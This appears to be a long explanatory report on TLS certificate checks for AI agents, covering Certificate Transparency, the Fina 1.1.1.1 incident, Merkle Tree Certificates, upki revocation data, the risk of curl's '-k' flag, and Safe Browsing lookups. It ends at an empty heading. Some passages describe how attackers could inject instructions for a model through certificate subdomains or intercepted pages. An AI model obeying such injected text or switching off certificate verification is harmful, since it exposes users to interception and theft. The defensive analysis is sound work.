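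The log could still keep two trees, showing one to the victim of an attack and the other to everybody else. Each tree would pass both tests, so someone has to compare the roots that different people receive. Google Chrome's *Certificate Transparency* policy for log operators says that Google tests whether logs are "consistent from every point of view". Chrome also began auditing timestamps in March 2021. *Chrome Removes “One Google Log” Requirement from Its CT Policy* (Ristić, 2022) reports that Chrome required every certificate to be in at least one log run by Google until 2022, when it dropped the rule as the auditing improved.

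### Logs, monitors and browsers

A log stores certificates and a browser checks for timestamps, but neither checks whether the domain's owner asked for the certificate. Owners can find certificates they didn't ask for by using a monitor, a service that downloads new log entries and looks for particular names. They can run their own monitor or use a company that sends them alerts.

| | Who runs it | What it does | What it cannot tell |
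|---|---|---|---|
| Log | Browser makers, CAs and other companies | Records certificates and signs timestamps and roots | Whether a certificate was issued to the right party |
| Monitor | Domain owners, or a service working for them | Searches the logs for certificates that an owner did not order | Whether someone has used a certificate in an attack |
| Browser | The user | Rejects certificates without enough timestamps | Whether anyone has looked at the log entry |

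This arrangement has worked well overall. Chromium's *Certificate Transparency* credits the logs with exposing problems at a large number of CAs, many of which had not noticed them. But the arrangement depends on owners checking the logs, and a wrong certificate remains usable until somebody acts.

### Twelve certificates for 1.1.1.1

Cloudflare runs a public DNS resolver at 1.1.1.1, which millions of devices use for name lookups. About 60% of the queries arrive unencrypted. The rest can use TLS, which requires the resolver to have a certificate. Most certificates contain a domain name, but a device cannot look up its resolver's name before it has a resolver. It connects directly to the IP address, so the certificate has to contain that address.

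Cloudflare's *Addressing the unauthorized issuance of multiple TLS certificates for 1.1.1.1* (2025) reports that Fina issued the certificates while testing its issuing system with its production keys, which other people's software trusted. Fina later blamed a mistake in entering IP addresses. Each certificate was valid for a year and also contained names such as test1.hr. Most of these names were unregistered, so Fina cannot have checked that anyone controlled them. One certificate that Cloudflare reproduces was issued to a fictional company called "TEST D.D."

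Fina revoked five of the twelve certificates within 33 minutes, but the other seven stayed in force for periods ranging from nine days to more than three months. On the morning of 18 July 2025, it revoked one certificate for 1.1.1.1, issued a second four minutes later, revoked that one, and then issued a third, which it left in place until September. Staff evidently knew how to revoke a test certificate but did not see the address as a problem.

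To exploit one of these certificates, an attacker would have needed its private key, a victim whose software trusted Fina, and a way to intercept traffic between that victim and Cloudflare. Fina said that the keys never left its systems and that it had destroyed them, but Cloudflare could not verify this. Microsoft's root store trusted Fina, but those of Chrome, Android, Apple and Mozilla did not, which ruled out attacks on most phones and many browsers. Cloudflare searched past routing announcements for a hijack of 1.1.1.1 and found none, but it could not have seen an interception closer to the user.

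An attacker who met all three conditions could have read a victim's DNS lookups and returned false addresses, though certificate checks would still have helped protect visits to HTTPS sites. The greater danger on Windows was that Fina, like DigiNotar, could issue certificates for any site.

### Why nobody noticed for eighteen months

Someone posted about a possibly misissued certificate on the forum Hacker News on 1 September 2025. Cloudflare then received two reports through its programme for security researchers, but its staff misjudged both. Cloudflare started investigating on 3 September, after Zhang (2025), in *Incident Report*, publicly listed three certificates that were still valid. Microsoft began blocking the certificates that evening, and Fina had revoked them all by the next morning.

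Cloudflare was unusually well placed to find the certificates earlier, because it operates CT logs and sells a monitoring service that alerts customers to certificates for their domains. It gives three reasons for missing them. The service did not send alerts for certificates issued to IP addresses. Even for ordinary domain names, Cloudflare had not built good enough filters, and it ordered too many certificates for staff to review the alerts by hand. It also had not turned on alerts for all its domains because they were so noisy.

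The filtering problem is probably the most common of these. A small company with one website can recognise every certificate it has ordered, but a large company, where many teams and suppliers order certificates, can only pick out a wrongly issued one if it keeps a reliable list of those it ordered.

Others had not been watching Fina closely either. People replying to Zhang soon found a certificate for 2.2.2.2, an address assigned to Oracle, and others for private network addresses and for names containing spaces, which are not allowed. A Mozilla employee confirmed in the same discussion that Firefox had never trusted Fina. This may explain the lack of scrutiny, as browser makers have little reason to examine a CA they do not trust.

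Cloudflare called the detection "a lucky one". Browsers require certificates to be logged, but most DNS clients do not, and these certificates were mainly useful against DNS clients. If Fina had kept its test certificates out of the logs, they would have worked just as well against those clients, and Cloudflare would have had no way to find them. Fina's explanation seemed to treat publication in the logs as part of the error. Cloudflare replied that publishing test certificates is correct and that the mistake was signing for an address without its owner's permission.

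### Could an agent require timestamps itself?

An agent that drives Chrome or Firefox benefits from the browser's timestamp check. Most non-browser clients have no such check, although the upki project, covered in the next section, is meant to help. In principle, a developer could write a check that extracts the timestamps from the certificate, verifies each signature with the log's public key, and counts the log operators.

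The difficulty is keeping the list of logs up to date. *End of Life Plan for RFC 6962 Certificate Transparency Logs* (Aas, 2025) announced that Let's Encrypt, a large CA that issues free certificates, would stop adding certificates to its older logs and shut them down on 28 February 2026. Let's Encrypt delayed the change until browsers fully trusted the replacement logs. An agent with a list from before the change would not recognise timestamps from the new logs and might reject honest sites.

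An outdated list of Certificate Transparency (CT) logs can make a browser reject good certificates, so browsers stop enforcing CT when their list gets too old. Chrome and Firefox stop after 70 days without an update, and Apple's devices stop after 60. An Apple employee confirmed the 60-day limit in *Question Regarding CT Log List Validity in Apple’s CT Policy*, a discussion started by Tong (2026). An agent running in a container that nobody has rebuilt for three months would face the same choice between rejecting good certificates and skipping the CT check.

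Existing code may not solve the problem. Google Chrome's *Certificate Transparency* guidance for developers describes frozen log lists that keep applications working when they rely on CT libraries. Anyone can download the private keys of two imitation logs on these lists, so a certificate can pass the check without appearing in any real log. Google warns that the lists provide no protection. *ChromeCtPolicy* describes another library as following Chrome's policy, but that library still requires one timestamp from a Google log, so it rejects some certificates that Chrome has accepted since 2022.

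A well-maintained check for log timestamps would help against a stolen or guessed CA key, as in the eMudhra case. Someone who used such a key to sign a certificate for a bank would have to submit it to the logs before the agent accepted it, and the bank's monitor could then find it. The agent would still accept the certificate in the meantime, because the check makes attacks easier to discover but mostly relies on other people to discover them. The check also would not have given the agent a reason to reject Fina's certificates, since Fina had logged them.

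### What a domain's certificate history reveals

Anyone can also search the logs by name, for example on crt.sh, a free site run by Sectigo. An agent could look up a shop's domain to see when it first got a certificate, which CAs have issued certificates for it, and which subdomains they covered. The page cannot change this record. If a ticket seller claims to have been in business since 1998 but its domain got its first certificate last week, the agent has good reason to ask the user before paying.

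A clean history is much weaker evidence. The logs would record a certificate for fiffa.com as they would any other. A fraudster can register a domain a year ahead, let a free program renew its certificate every couple of months, and end up with a history that looks like that of a small honest business. Genuine new shops, meanwhile, have short histories. An established site can also distribute malware, as DAEMON Tools and JDownloader both did, without needing to change its certificates.

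Shared hosting makes certificate logs harder to interpret. When a hosting company covers all its customers with one wildcard certificate, such as one for *.example.com, the logs show the host's history but nothing about an individual customer.

An agent also cannot easily spot a wrongly issued certificate in a certificate history. A new CA might indicate an attack, but companies often change CAs. Cloudflare struggled to pick out bad certificates among its own, and an outsider does not have a list of the certificates the company ordered. The name "TEST D.D." would have looked suspicious to a careful reader, but an attacker would choose a more plausible one.

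The logs help agents indirectly. Companies search them for new domain names that resemble their own and ask hosts to take down the imitations. Makers of blocklists can search them too. Since a phishing site usually needs a certificate before it opens, these searches can give defenders a short head start. An agent that queries the logs directly should use ordinary code to extract the dates and pass only those to the model, because applicants choose their own subdomains and an attacker could use one to put instructions for the model in a certificate.

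### Merkle Tree Certificates

CT was added to a system in which CAs could already issue certificates without telling anyone. A new design, Merkle Tree Certificates (MTCs), makes logging part of issuing. The immediate reason for the design is that signatures able to withstand quantum computers are large. A common signature today takes 64 bytes, while one made with ML-DSA-44, among the smaller post-quantum methods, takes 2,420. According to *A Post-Quantum Future for Let's Encrypt*, by ISRG, the non-profit that runs Let's Encrypt, a typical connection involves five signatures and two public keys. Replacing them all with post-quantum versions would push the opening exchange well past 10 kilobytes, and some connections would fail.

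The draft standard by Benjamin, O'Brien and colleagues (2026), in *Merkle Tree Certificates*, reverses the usual order. Instead of signing a certificate and then sending it to a log, each CA keeps a log of its own and issues a certificate by adding an entry to it. The earlier eight-entry tree can show how this works:

1. The CA checks control of eight names and adds eight entries to its log.
2. It signs the root, 46, which certifies all eight entries at once.
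3. Other organisations, called cosigners, confirm that the log has only grown since they last saw it, and sign the root too. Some of them, called mirrors, also keep a public copy of the log.
4. The site with the sixth entry receives its certificate, which consists of the entry's contents, the proof 61, 73, 76, and the signatures on 46.
5. A browser repeats the three calculations and checks the signatures on the result.

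The signatures in the example cover the whole log, but in practice the CA also signs smaller trees of recent entries, which keeps the proofs short.

An even smaller version has no signatures on the tree. The browser's maker sends trusted roots to the browser in the background, so the server only needs to send the contents and the proof to a browser that already has the root, 46. For a tree of about a million certificates, the proof is 640 bytes. Under the present system, the CA's signature and two timestamps would take 7,260 bytes with ML-DSA-44. A browser with outdated roots can use the version with signatures.

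Google's *Cultivating a robust and efficient quantum-safe HTTPS* (2026) says that it is impossible to issue an MTC without including it in a public tree. This depends on the cosigners as well as the mathematics, since a CA could sign a tree and show it to nobody. Chrome therefore plans to require one signature from the CA and another from a mirror run by a different organisation (DeBlasio, 2026, *Welcome to mtcs@, and what we hope MTCs will look like*). Apple's policy requires three cosignatures, according to Ivezic's *Apple MTC Policy Raises the Bar for Post-Quantum PKI* (2026).

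MTCs would close the gap that made Cloudflare call itself lucky. A DNS client or Python library that accepts MTCs must check the proof and the cosignatures to validate the certificate, so it could not skip the logging check as most such programs do now. But MTCs would not have stopped Fina from issuing the certificates. Fina would have added an entry for 1.1.1.1 to its log, the mirror would have copied it, and Cloudflare would still have had to notice it.

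Shorter lifetimes might have helped more. Chrome intends to accept MTCs that last at most 47 days and strongly encourages seven. With a seven-day limit, even the last of Fina's certificates, issued on 26 August, would have expired on 2 September, the day before Zhang's report. The maximum lifetime of conventional certificates is also due to fall to 47 days by March 2029, so this benefit does not depend entirely on the new design.

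Google is also considering having CAs publish their proof that an applicant controlled a name, so that anyone could check it. This would address what Fina did wrong. At present, a log entry shows that Fina signed for 1.1.1.1, but outsiders cannot see what check, if any, Fina made first. Google lists the change as something to explore and has not given a date.

MTCs could make it harder for agents to read a domain's history. Benjamin and colleagues allow logs to delete entries for certificates that expired long ago, to keep the logs small. In Chrome's test programme, entries only have to remain available for 14 days after the certificate expires (Clements, 2026, *Chrome MTC Testing and Validation Trust Store*). Unless monitors keep their own archives, the date of a domain's first certificate could become impossible to find.

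### Where the 2027 rollout stands

Google announced a three-stage plan in February 2026. The first stage is an experiment with Cloudflare on real traffic, in which a conventional certificate backs up every MTC. *First External Operators Apply to Chrome’s Post-Quantum Certificate Test Program* (Ivezic, 2026) reports that the experiment covers about 1,000 domains and still uses today's signature methods. In the first quarter of 2027, Google plans to invite established operators of CT logs to help start public MTCs. In the third quarter, it plans to open a separate Chrome root store for MTCs to more CAs.

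Preparations were on course in the autumn of 2026, but production had not begun. The Shanghai CA TrustAsia applied to join Chrome's test programme in July, followed by the security firm Geomys. Let's Encrypt was aiming for a test service in late 2026 and a production-ready one in 2027. Cloudflare's *Building a post-quantum certificate authority with Merkle Tree Certificates* (2026) announced the company's own new CA in September. Zorz (2026), in *Post-quantum website certificates from Cloudflare are scheduled for early 2027*, reports that production is scheduled to start in the first quarter of 2027. Cloudflare's applications to the Chrome, Apple, Microsoft and Mozilla root programmes were all still pending.

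The draft standard is a more serious risk to the schedule. Version 05, from July 2026, changed the structure of the tree and the relationship between CAs and cosigners, so developers who built on earlier versions may have to redo some of their work.

Programs outside browsers will probably take longer to support MTCs. Their TLS libraries need new code, a list of trusted cosigners and, for the smallest certificates, regular updates with new roots. Servers can keep a conventional certificate for clients that do not support MTCs, so an agent using an older library should still connect to most sites. But Google plans to let sites refuse this fallback in Chrome from the third stage, and it does not currently intend to add conventional certificates with post-quantum signatures to Chrome's root store. An agent that needs a quantum-resistant connection to a public website may therefore have to support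 MTCs.

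## The upki project and the certificate checks that programs outside browsers lack

Browser makers send their browsers new security data throughout the day, including lists of revoked certificates, blocked certificate authorities (CAs) and approved logs. An agent that fetches pages with curl or a language library gets almost none of this. upki, a project announced in December 2025, aims to supply the same data to every program on a Linux computer. So far it covers revocation, a CA's withdrawal of a certificate before it expires.

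### What curl checks and what it skips

| Check | Firefox and Chrome | curl and common libraries on Linux, by default |
|---|---|---|
| Signatures lead to a trusted root | Yes | Yes |
| Certificate contains the host name | Yes | Yes |
| Certificate has not expired | Yes | Yes |
| CA has not revoked the certificate | Firefox checks all known revocations, Chrome about 1% of them | No, except curl on Ubuntu 26.10 |
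| Certificate has timestamps from public logs | Yes | No |
| Emergency block on a CA | Arrives within hours | Arrives with a software update |
| Server left out an intermediate certificate | Browser supplies it | Connection fails |

The first three checks are enough to expose an impostor without a valid certificate, such as the GRU's fake Outlook server. The next three matter when someone has stolen a site's key or a CA has failed. *Eight Bits of Trust; eMudhra's CA keys cracked in milliseconds* (Helme, 2026) lists curl, Python, Node.js, Go, Java and git among the clients that check neither revocation nor logs by default. Helme is particularly worried about tools that people install by downloading a script over HTTPS and running it without checking a signature. An attacker with a forged certificate could replace the script. Coding agents often install software this way, sometimes on machines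 that hold passwords for cloud services.

The weak keys at eMudhra in October 2026 showed how slowly an emergency block reaches programs outside browsers. Firefox blocked the certificates on 17 October. The developers of the programming language Go heard about the problem only on 19 October, first from an outside researcher and then from Mozilla. Go leaves certificate checks to the operating system on Windows and macOS but uses its own code on Linux. *Our Response To The eMudhra Key Disclosure Incident* describes how the Go team wrote a block into that code and released it about seven and a half hours after the first warning. Developers then had to rebuild each Go program with the new version before the block took effect.

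Most Linux programs rely on a plain file of trusted roots, which provides no way to reject a single intermediate. Ubuntu, a widely used version of Linux, therefore had to remove whole roots. According to its *eMudhra CA compromise fixes available*, Ubuntu removed two on 20 October and warned that some honest sites might become unreachable. Its newer releases had already dropped one of the two. Computers with automatic updates received the change within a day.

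Other copies of the file last much longer. Python programs often come with their own copy, and a container, the sealed environment in which many agents run, keeps the file it was built with. Mac users can delete the eMudhra roots from the file that curl and python3 read, but *eMudhra Intermediate CA Compromise* repeats a warning that a macOS update may restore them.

The problem in the last row of the table affects honest sites. A server should send its own certificate and the intermediates that link it to a root, but many administrators forget the intermediates. They rarely notice, because Firefox stores copies of all known intermediates and Chrome downloads any that are missing. *An update on upki* explains that curl does neither and reports an unknown issuer. An agent using curl therefore reports a certificate error for a site that works in the user's browser.

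### Why revocation did not work for so long

Suppose a thief copies the private key of shop.example.com. The owner reports this, and the CA revokes the certificate. But the certificate does not change, so a client has to learn about the revocation from another source.

The oldest method is the certificate revocation list (CRL), a signed list of the serial numbers of certificates that a CA has revoked. The client downloads the list from an address in the certificate, checks the CA's signature and the date, and searches for the certificate's serial number. APNIC's *Revocation of X.509 certificates* (2026) examines a Let's Encrypt list that had 1,562 entries and was valid for nine days, so a client with a stored copy could miss a new revocation for more than a week. There are about 3,000 of these lists, with a combined size of 300 MB. Few users would accept waiting for a download before each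 new site opened.

The Online Certificate Status Protocol (OCSP) replaced the download with a question about one certificate, which the client sent to the CA during the connection. This had three faults:

- **Delay.** Mozilla measured a median wait of 100 milliseconds.
- **Privacy.** The CA learned which sites each user visited. Most queries were unencrypted, so anyone on the route could learn this too.
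- **Ignored failures.** If no answer came, most clients connected anyway, because otherwise a fault at one CA would have made all its customers' sites unreachable.

The last fault let attackers defeat the check. To use a stolen certificate, an attacker usually has to intercept the victim's traffic, and someone in that position can also block the query to the CA. Adam Langley, who worked on Chrome's security at Google, called online checking useless for this reason, and Chrome stopped doing it in 2012.

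In a later variant called stapling, the server fetches the CA's signed answer and sends it with the certificate. This removes the delay and the privacy leak. But many servers never adopted it, so a client cannot treat a missing answer as a sign of attack.

In 2023 the CA/Browser Forum made OCSP optional and certificate revocation lists compulsory again. Let's Encrypt, which was answering about 340 billion OCSP queries a month at the start of 2025, shut down its OCSP service that August. Alden (2025), in *Linux's missing CRL infrastructure*, points out that Windows and macOS have a shared service that downloads revocation lists, but Linux had none, and few Linux programs fetched the lists themselves. Curl could make OCSP checks if the user turned them on, but these no longer worked for Let's Encrypt certificates.

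### How CRLite compresses the lists

Browser makers had meanwhile started collecting the lists themselves and sending the results to users. Chrome's version contains only the revocations judged most important, about 35,000 of some four million. Mozilla argues that nobody can reliably identify the important ones, because CAs give no reason for about half of all revocations and some of those probably involve stolen keys. Mozilla's *CRLite* describes a format compact enough to include every revocation.

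CRLite uses filters. A filter is a compact table that can test whether an item belongs to a set without storing the items themselves. It never misses a member, but it sometimes flags an item that does not belong. CRLite corrects these false alarms with a second filter. Take the four million revoked certificates and suppose, for easy arithmetic, that there are 1,024 million good ones:

1. The first filter uses 8 bits for each revoked certificate, or 4 MB in all. It flags every revoked certificate and, by chance, one good certificate in 2^8 = 256. That makes four million false alarms.
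2. Mozilla can work out in advance which certificates these are, because the public logs give it a list of all certificates. The second filter stores one bit for each of the eight million flagged certificates, with 1 for revoked and 0 for good. This takes another 1 MB.

The total is 5 MB. With *r* revoked certificates, *s* good ones and *k* bits per revoked certificate in the first filter, the two filters need about *rk* + *r* + *s*/2^*k* bits. Using 6 bits would raise the total to 5.5 MB, because a smaller first filter produces more false alarms for the second to store, and using 10 bits would raise it to about 5.6 MB.

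Mozilla's real filters also divide the certificates into groups, which saves more space. Firefox downloads a complete file of about 4 MB every 45 days and smaller updates every 12 hours, an average of 300 kB a day. The check needs no network request, so it reveals nothing about the user's browsing and an attacker cannot block it. As Mozilla moved 80% of Firefox's revocation checks to CRLite, the median time to set up a secure connection fell from 56.4 to 39.9 milliseconds. Mozilla turned on CRLite for all desktop users in Firefox 137, in 2025.

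The correction works only for certificates that Mozilla knew about when it built the filters. For any other certificate the result would be meaningless, so the software has to recognise that the data does not cover it. The data never covers certificates from a company's private CA, and it does not cover very new ones until the next update.

### What upki does today

Ellie Kanning, a Linux user, had asked the developers of three projects to provide a shared revocation list, but they all considered it outside their scope. One of the projects was OpenSSL, the encryption library behind much Linux software. Kanning told Alden that the situation was "an incident waiting to happen". A few months later, Canonical, the company behind Ubuntu, agreed to fund work on a solution by Dirkjan Ochtman and Joe Birr-Pixton, who maintain the encryption library rustls. *Addressing Linux's Missing PKI Infrastructure*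 announced the plan, which reuses Mozilla's CRLite files.

upki has four main parts. A mirror program copies the files from Mozilla to other servers, so that Linux computers do not depend on Mozilla's. A fetch program downloads them to each computer. A command-line tool checks individual certificates, and a set of libraries lets other programs make the same check while they connect.

The command-line tool is the easiest for an agent's developer to try. *Try the upki preview for Ubuntu* (2026) gives this example:

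`curl -sw '%{certs}' https://google.com | upki revocation check`

Curl opens the page and passes the site's certificates to upki, which prints `NotRevoked`. For a test site with a deliberately revoked certificate, it prints `CertainlyRevoked`. But curl sends its request before the result appears, so an agent should run the check before sending a password or anything else private.

Ubuntu 26.10, released on 15 October 2026, avoids this problem by building the check into curl. If a certificate is on the list, curl stops before it sends the request. *Ubuntu certificate revocation checks arrive in curl, OpenSSL is next* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that Ubuntu's developers ran the same command on versions 26.04 and 26.10. The older version connected to a site with a revoked certificate, and the newer one blocked the connection.

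Many agents will not benefit yet. Curl behaves as it did before until the first download of revocation data finishes. That download depends on a timer that refreshes the data every six hours. The timer runs in systemd, the program that manages background services on Ubuntu, and most containers do not run systemd. If a developer starts a new container for each task, curl may never have any revocation data unless the developer adds the fetch command to the setup. Ubuntu will support version 26.10 only until July 2027 (Ubuntu, 2026), so companies that prefer releases with long-term support will mostly still be using 26.04 or older.

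Ubuntu plans to build the upki check into its copy of OpenSSL for version 27.04, which would cover most of the more than 1,000 packages that use the library directly. Programs that replace OpenSSL's verification with their own or come with a separate copy of the library would still need changes. Go Proposals' unofficial tracker, *What's coming in Go*, lists a upki check for the next version of Go as finished on 30 November.

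### What upki would have done about eMudhra

The current version of upki would probably not have stopped a certificate forged with one of eMudhra's keys. CRLite covers website certificates in the public logs, and an attacker could have kept a forged one out of them. Mozilla blocks intermediate certificates through a separate list, OneCRL, which upki does not use yet.

Adding that list is next on the roadmap in upki's funding proposal. A block would then reach every connected program at the next update, and Ubuntu could stop one intermediate without removing a whole root. After that, the developers plan to have upki download the tree roots that the smallest Merkle Tree Certificates require, and they have applied for funding for this work.

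The project plans two more features but has not set a date for either. One would require timestamps from public logs, with upki keeping the list of approved logs current. The other would store the known intermediate certificates, as Firefox does. Storing them would remove a common cause of certificate errors on legitimate sites, but it would not add protection against forged certificates.

### Shorter lifetimes as an alternative

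A client that never checks revocation still checks the expiry date. If certificates expire soon enough, the client stops accepting a stolen one without having to learn about the theft. The CA/Browser Forum has adopted this schedule for new certificates:

| Issued from | Maximum lifetime |
|---|---|
| September 2020 | 398 days |
| 15 March 2026 | 200 days |
| 15 March 2027 | 100 days |
| 15 March 2029 | 47 days |

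Some certificates will expire much sooner. Let's Encrypt already offers one that lasts six days, and Apple has said it will limit Merkle Tree Certificates to seven days.

The benefit depends on when a site replaces its certificate. Ristić (2026), in *Get Ready for Seven-Day Certificates*, expects sites to replace a 47-day certificate after 30 days and a seven-day certificate after four. If a thief is equally likely to copy the key at any point before the replacement, the 47-day certificate has between 17 and 47 days left, or 32 on average, and the seven-day certificate has five on average. CAs must revoke a certificate within 24 hours of getting evidence that its key was stolen, so a client with CRLite or upki could reject either certificate within a day or two of the owner reporting the theft.

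APNIC's article argues that the move to 47 days is unlikely to achieve much, because attackers now finish their work in minutes or hours and a month is about as useful to them as a year. This criticism is fair for 47-day certificates but less so for seven-day ones, and it does not account for attackers who want to read someone's traffic for months. Kanning objected that large companies outside the technology industry would not adopt short-lived certificates. They will have little choice about the 47-day limit, since no CA that browsers trust may issue anything longer, but they can still avoid six-day and seven-day certificates.

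Short lifetimes also fail if the site keeps its old key when it renews its certificate. Certificates are public, so a thief with the key can download the new one and use it. Short lifetimes help only if the owner creates a new key at each renewal and the thief no longer has access to the server. They also don't limit someone who has a CA's key. A forger with an eMudhra key could have written any expiry date into a certificate, and curl does not reject certificates for lasting too long.

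Short certificate lifetimes also give administrators of legitimate sites less time to fix a failed renewal. If the automatic renewal of a seven-day certificate breaks on day four, the administrator has three days to repair it, perhaps including a weekend. Agents may therefore encounter more expired certificates on sites that nobody has attacked.

### Retrying with verification switched off

An agent that gets a certificate error can usually bypass it by turning off certificate verification. Curl has the option `-k`, Python's requests library has `verify=False`, and git and Node.js have equivalent settings. The connection is still encrypted, but the client accepts any certificate.

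Suppose a coding agent has to download a library from a supplier's site. The server does not send its intermediate certificate, so curl reports an error. The agent knows from many forum posts that `-k` gets past the error, so it adds the flag and gets the file. This is harmless here because the site is honest. But an attacker intercepting the connection would cause a similar error, and retrying with `-k` would download the attacker's file. The attacker could also change any page the agent read over that connection and insert instructions for the model.

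Human programmers have made this mistake for years, sometimes by accident. In 2012, researchers at Stanford and the University of Texas at Austin found that an Amazon payment library had set curl's name check to "true". The setting took a number, and the correct value was 2. Curl read "true" as 1, which turned off the comparison of names, and the library kept working normally.

An agent can often use a safer fix if its developer has prepared one. When an intermediate is missing, a program can download it from the address given in the site's certificate and verify the whole chain as usual. This is safe even if someone tampers with the download, because a false intermediate would not lead to a trusted root. Many companies inspect their employees' traffic with a proxy that presents certificates from the company's own CA. Adding that CA to the agent's root store removes the error and leaves verification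 on. If a certificate has expired, has been revoked or contains the wrong name, the agent has no similar fix and should stop and tell the user.

An agent may use `-k` despite a written instruction not to, because it can forget the instruction or follow an injected one instead. Searching its commands for `-k` is also unreliable, since the agent can write a script in another language that skips the certificate check. Putting the check where the agent cannot change it is more reliable. The developer can block direct connections to the internet and send all traffic through a proxy that verifies every site's certificate. If the agent then uses `-k`, it turns off only the check between itself and the proxy, and the proxy still refuses to connect to an impostor site.

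For Meta's personal agent, Muse, such a check could run in the component that controls the agent's network traffic. Ristić's newsletter describes this component as separate from the virtual machine where the agent runs. A proxy of this kind can read everything the agent sends, including passwords, so the developer has to protect it. It also needs current roots and revocation data, or every agent behind it will accept the same bad certificates.

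## Google Safe Browsing and lists of dangerous sites

Certificate checks do not detect dishonest operators, so browsers also consult a blocklist. Chrome, Safari and Firefox use Google Safe Browsing, the most widely used list, which protects more than five billion devices according to Google (2024). Microsoft's Edge uses a separate list, SmartScreen. Both lists miss most new scams. When researchers found 4,042 scam sites in October 2026, Chrome initially blocked only 16% of them.

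### How a page gets onto the list

Google has to learn that a page exists and then decide whether it is dangerous. *PhishTime* (Oest, Safaei and colleagues, 2020) calls these steps discovery and detection. Addresses come from the public, companies whose brands criminals imitate, and systems that monitor spam and web traffic. Google's crawlers visit the page, and if its content confirms the suspicion, Google adds the address to the list. Google cannot list every reported page, because a wrong entry can cut off an honest business from most of its visitors.

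Most reports contain only the page's address, so nothing happens if the page looks harmless when the crawler visits. In one of Oest and colleagues' experiments, Google listed 20% of test pages after ordinary reports and 91% after reports through a Chrome extension that also sends evidence such as a screenshot. The reports with evidence took longer to have an effect, with a median of about ten hours.

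### One lookup, step by step

Suppose an intruder has hidden a fake bank login in the `/orders/` folder of an honest shop, and Google has listed that folder. An agent receives the link `https://Shop.Example.com//orders/./view?id=42#top`. The client that checks it follows the rules in Google's *URLs and Hashing*:

1. **Normalise the address.** The client removes `#top`, changes the host name to lower case, and cleans up the extra slash and dot in the path. This leaves `shop.example.com/orders/view?id=42`. Without this step, an attacker could get around the list by adding a slash.
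2. **Form the variants.** The client combines each possible host with each possible path, which gives eight variants here:

```
shop.example.com/orders/view?id=42    example.com/orders/view?id=42
shop.example.com/orders/view          example.com/orders/view
shop.example.com/orders/              example.com/orders/
shop.example.com/                     example.com/
```

3. **Hash them.** The client calculates the SHA-256 hash of each variant and keeps the first four of its 32 bytes. Say that the hash of `shop.example.com/orders/` begins with `9f3c07e1`.
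4. **Compare the short prefixes.** The client looks for the eight prefixes in a list it has downloaded from Google. If none is there, it opens the page. In this case it finds `9f3c07e1`.
5. **Fetch the full hashes.** Two addresses can share a prefix, so the client sends `9f3c07e1` to Google and receives every listed hash that begins with it. One of them matches the full hash of `shop.example.com/orders/`, and the client displays a warning.

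The variants let Google list a whole domain, a subdomain, a folder or a single page. For each address, the client combines up to five hosts with up to six paths, which gives at most 30 variants. The client never tries a shared ending from the Public Suffix List, such as co.uk, as a host.

False matches in step 4 are uncommon. A four-byte prefix can take 2^32 values, or about 4.3 billion. If the downloaded list has four million prefixes, a harmless variant has about a 0.09% chance of matching one of them, and a harmless address with eight variants has about a 0.75% chance of at least one match.

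### What the short prefix hides

Google learns much less from a four-byte hash prefix than it would from the address itself. If the web has a trillion addresses, each prefix matches about 230 of them. Google also cannot use the prefix to recover a secret in the address's parameters, such as the code in a password-reset link.

The prefix hides the domain less well. There are only a few hundred million registered domains, so Google could hash the front-page address of each one and would usually find only one domain that matches a given front-page prefix. Several prefixes from the same address narrow the search further. This mattered little when clients contacted Google only after a local match, but newer versions of the check contact Google much more often.

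### Real-time checks through a relay

Chrome used to update its local list of dangerous sites every 30 to 60 minutes, according to Vumetric's *Google Introduces Enhanced Real-Time URL Protection for Chrome Users* (2024). AlternativeTo's *Google enhances Chrome's Safe Browsing with real-time privacy-preserving URL protection* reports that Google estimated the average malicious site existed for less than ten minutes. Many sites could therefore appear and disappear between updates. In March 2024, Chrome began to query Google's server when a user visits a site. Google expected this to block 25% more phishing.

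Version 5 of the Safe Browsing protocol offers the same method to other programs. The older method contacts Google only if an address resembles a dangerous one. Google's *Real Time Mode* describes a client that contacts Google unless the address is on a downloaded list of probably harmless sites or the client still has a recent answer for it. The check returns UNSAFE if a full hash matches and SAFE if none does. If the client cannot reach the server, the check returns UNSURE and the client uses its local list of threats instead.

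Chrome sends these queries through a relay run by the network company Fastly to keep Google from linking them to a person. Chrome encrypts the prefixes so that only Google can read them. Fastly knows the user's IP address but does not pass it to Google. 9to5Google quotes Google's conclusion that no single party has both the IP address and the prefixes. This protection depends on the two companies not combining their records.

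### How much the list catches

The best results come from 2019 tests in which Oest and colleagues created 2,862 harmless imitations of PayPal phishing pages and reported them to blocklist operators. Google listed 93% of the simplest pages, typically after about an hour. But Chrome and Safari on phones blocked only 58% of the same pages, and redirecting visitors through another address increased the delay in listing to nearly three hours.

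Later studies of real phishing pages found much lower rates. In *7 Days Later*, Lee, Lim and colleagues (2025) visited each of 286,237 phishing addresses from an industry feed every 30 minutes. Google listed 18.4% of them. The median time to listing was 5.8 hours, but some entries came so late that the mean was 108.7 hours. In 84% of cases, the site had gone offline before Google listed it. The researchers used the downloadable list, so Chrome's real-time check may have blocked some pages earlier.

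*INFERMAL* (2025) reports even shorter lifetimes. Its sampled phishing domains stayed online for about an hour on average, whether or not the researchers had complained to the registrar. A list that takes several hours to add such a site protects hardly any of the site's victims.

*ReDence* (Kaur, Horáček and colleagues, 2026) reports the most recent figures. Between 1 and 28 October 2026, the researchers took new domains from the public certificate logs and had an AI system investigate the 552,809 that led to working websites. They then confirmed 4,042 scams by hand. As soon as the system found a scam, the researchers reported it to Google and began opening it repeatedly in Chrome with the browser's strongest protection turned on.

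| Type of scam | Sites | Blocked at first | Blocked within a week | Median delay if blocked later |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Posing as a bank or card company | 374 | 44.1% | 69.8% | 30 hours |
| Technical support | 161 | 34.2% | 58.4% | 43 hours |
| Investment | 473 | 13.3% | 29.0% | 78 hours |
| Online shopping | 793 | 12.5% | 26.7% | 96 hours |
| Home improvement | 83 | 4.8% | 12.0% | 142 hours |
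| All 17 types | 4,042 | 16.3% | 33.0% | |

Chrome initially blocked 44.1% of the sites that tried to steal login details and 7.9% of the others. The lower rate is a problem for shopping agents, because a fake shop doesn't need the customer's password. SmartScreen, Norton and Malwarebytes had similar results at first, and all four services together caught only 27.5%.

These scams are harder for a crawler to recognise than a copy of PayPal's login page. Kaur and colleagues describe a fake prize draw with the logo of the retailer DICK'S Sporting Goods. It asked for card details only after the visitor had completed a survey, chosen a gift box and filled in a shipping form. A crawler that looked only at the first page would have found no form asking for a password or card number.

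The study probably understates how well the list protects people over a scam's whole life, because the study found many sites just after they opened. It also could not count scams the AI system missed.

### LayerX's test of AI browsers

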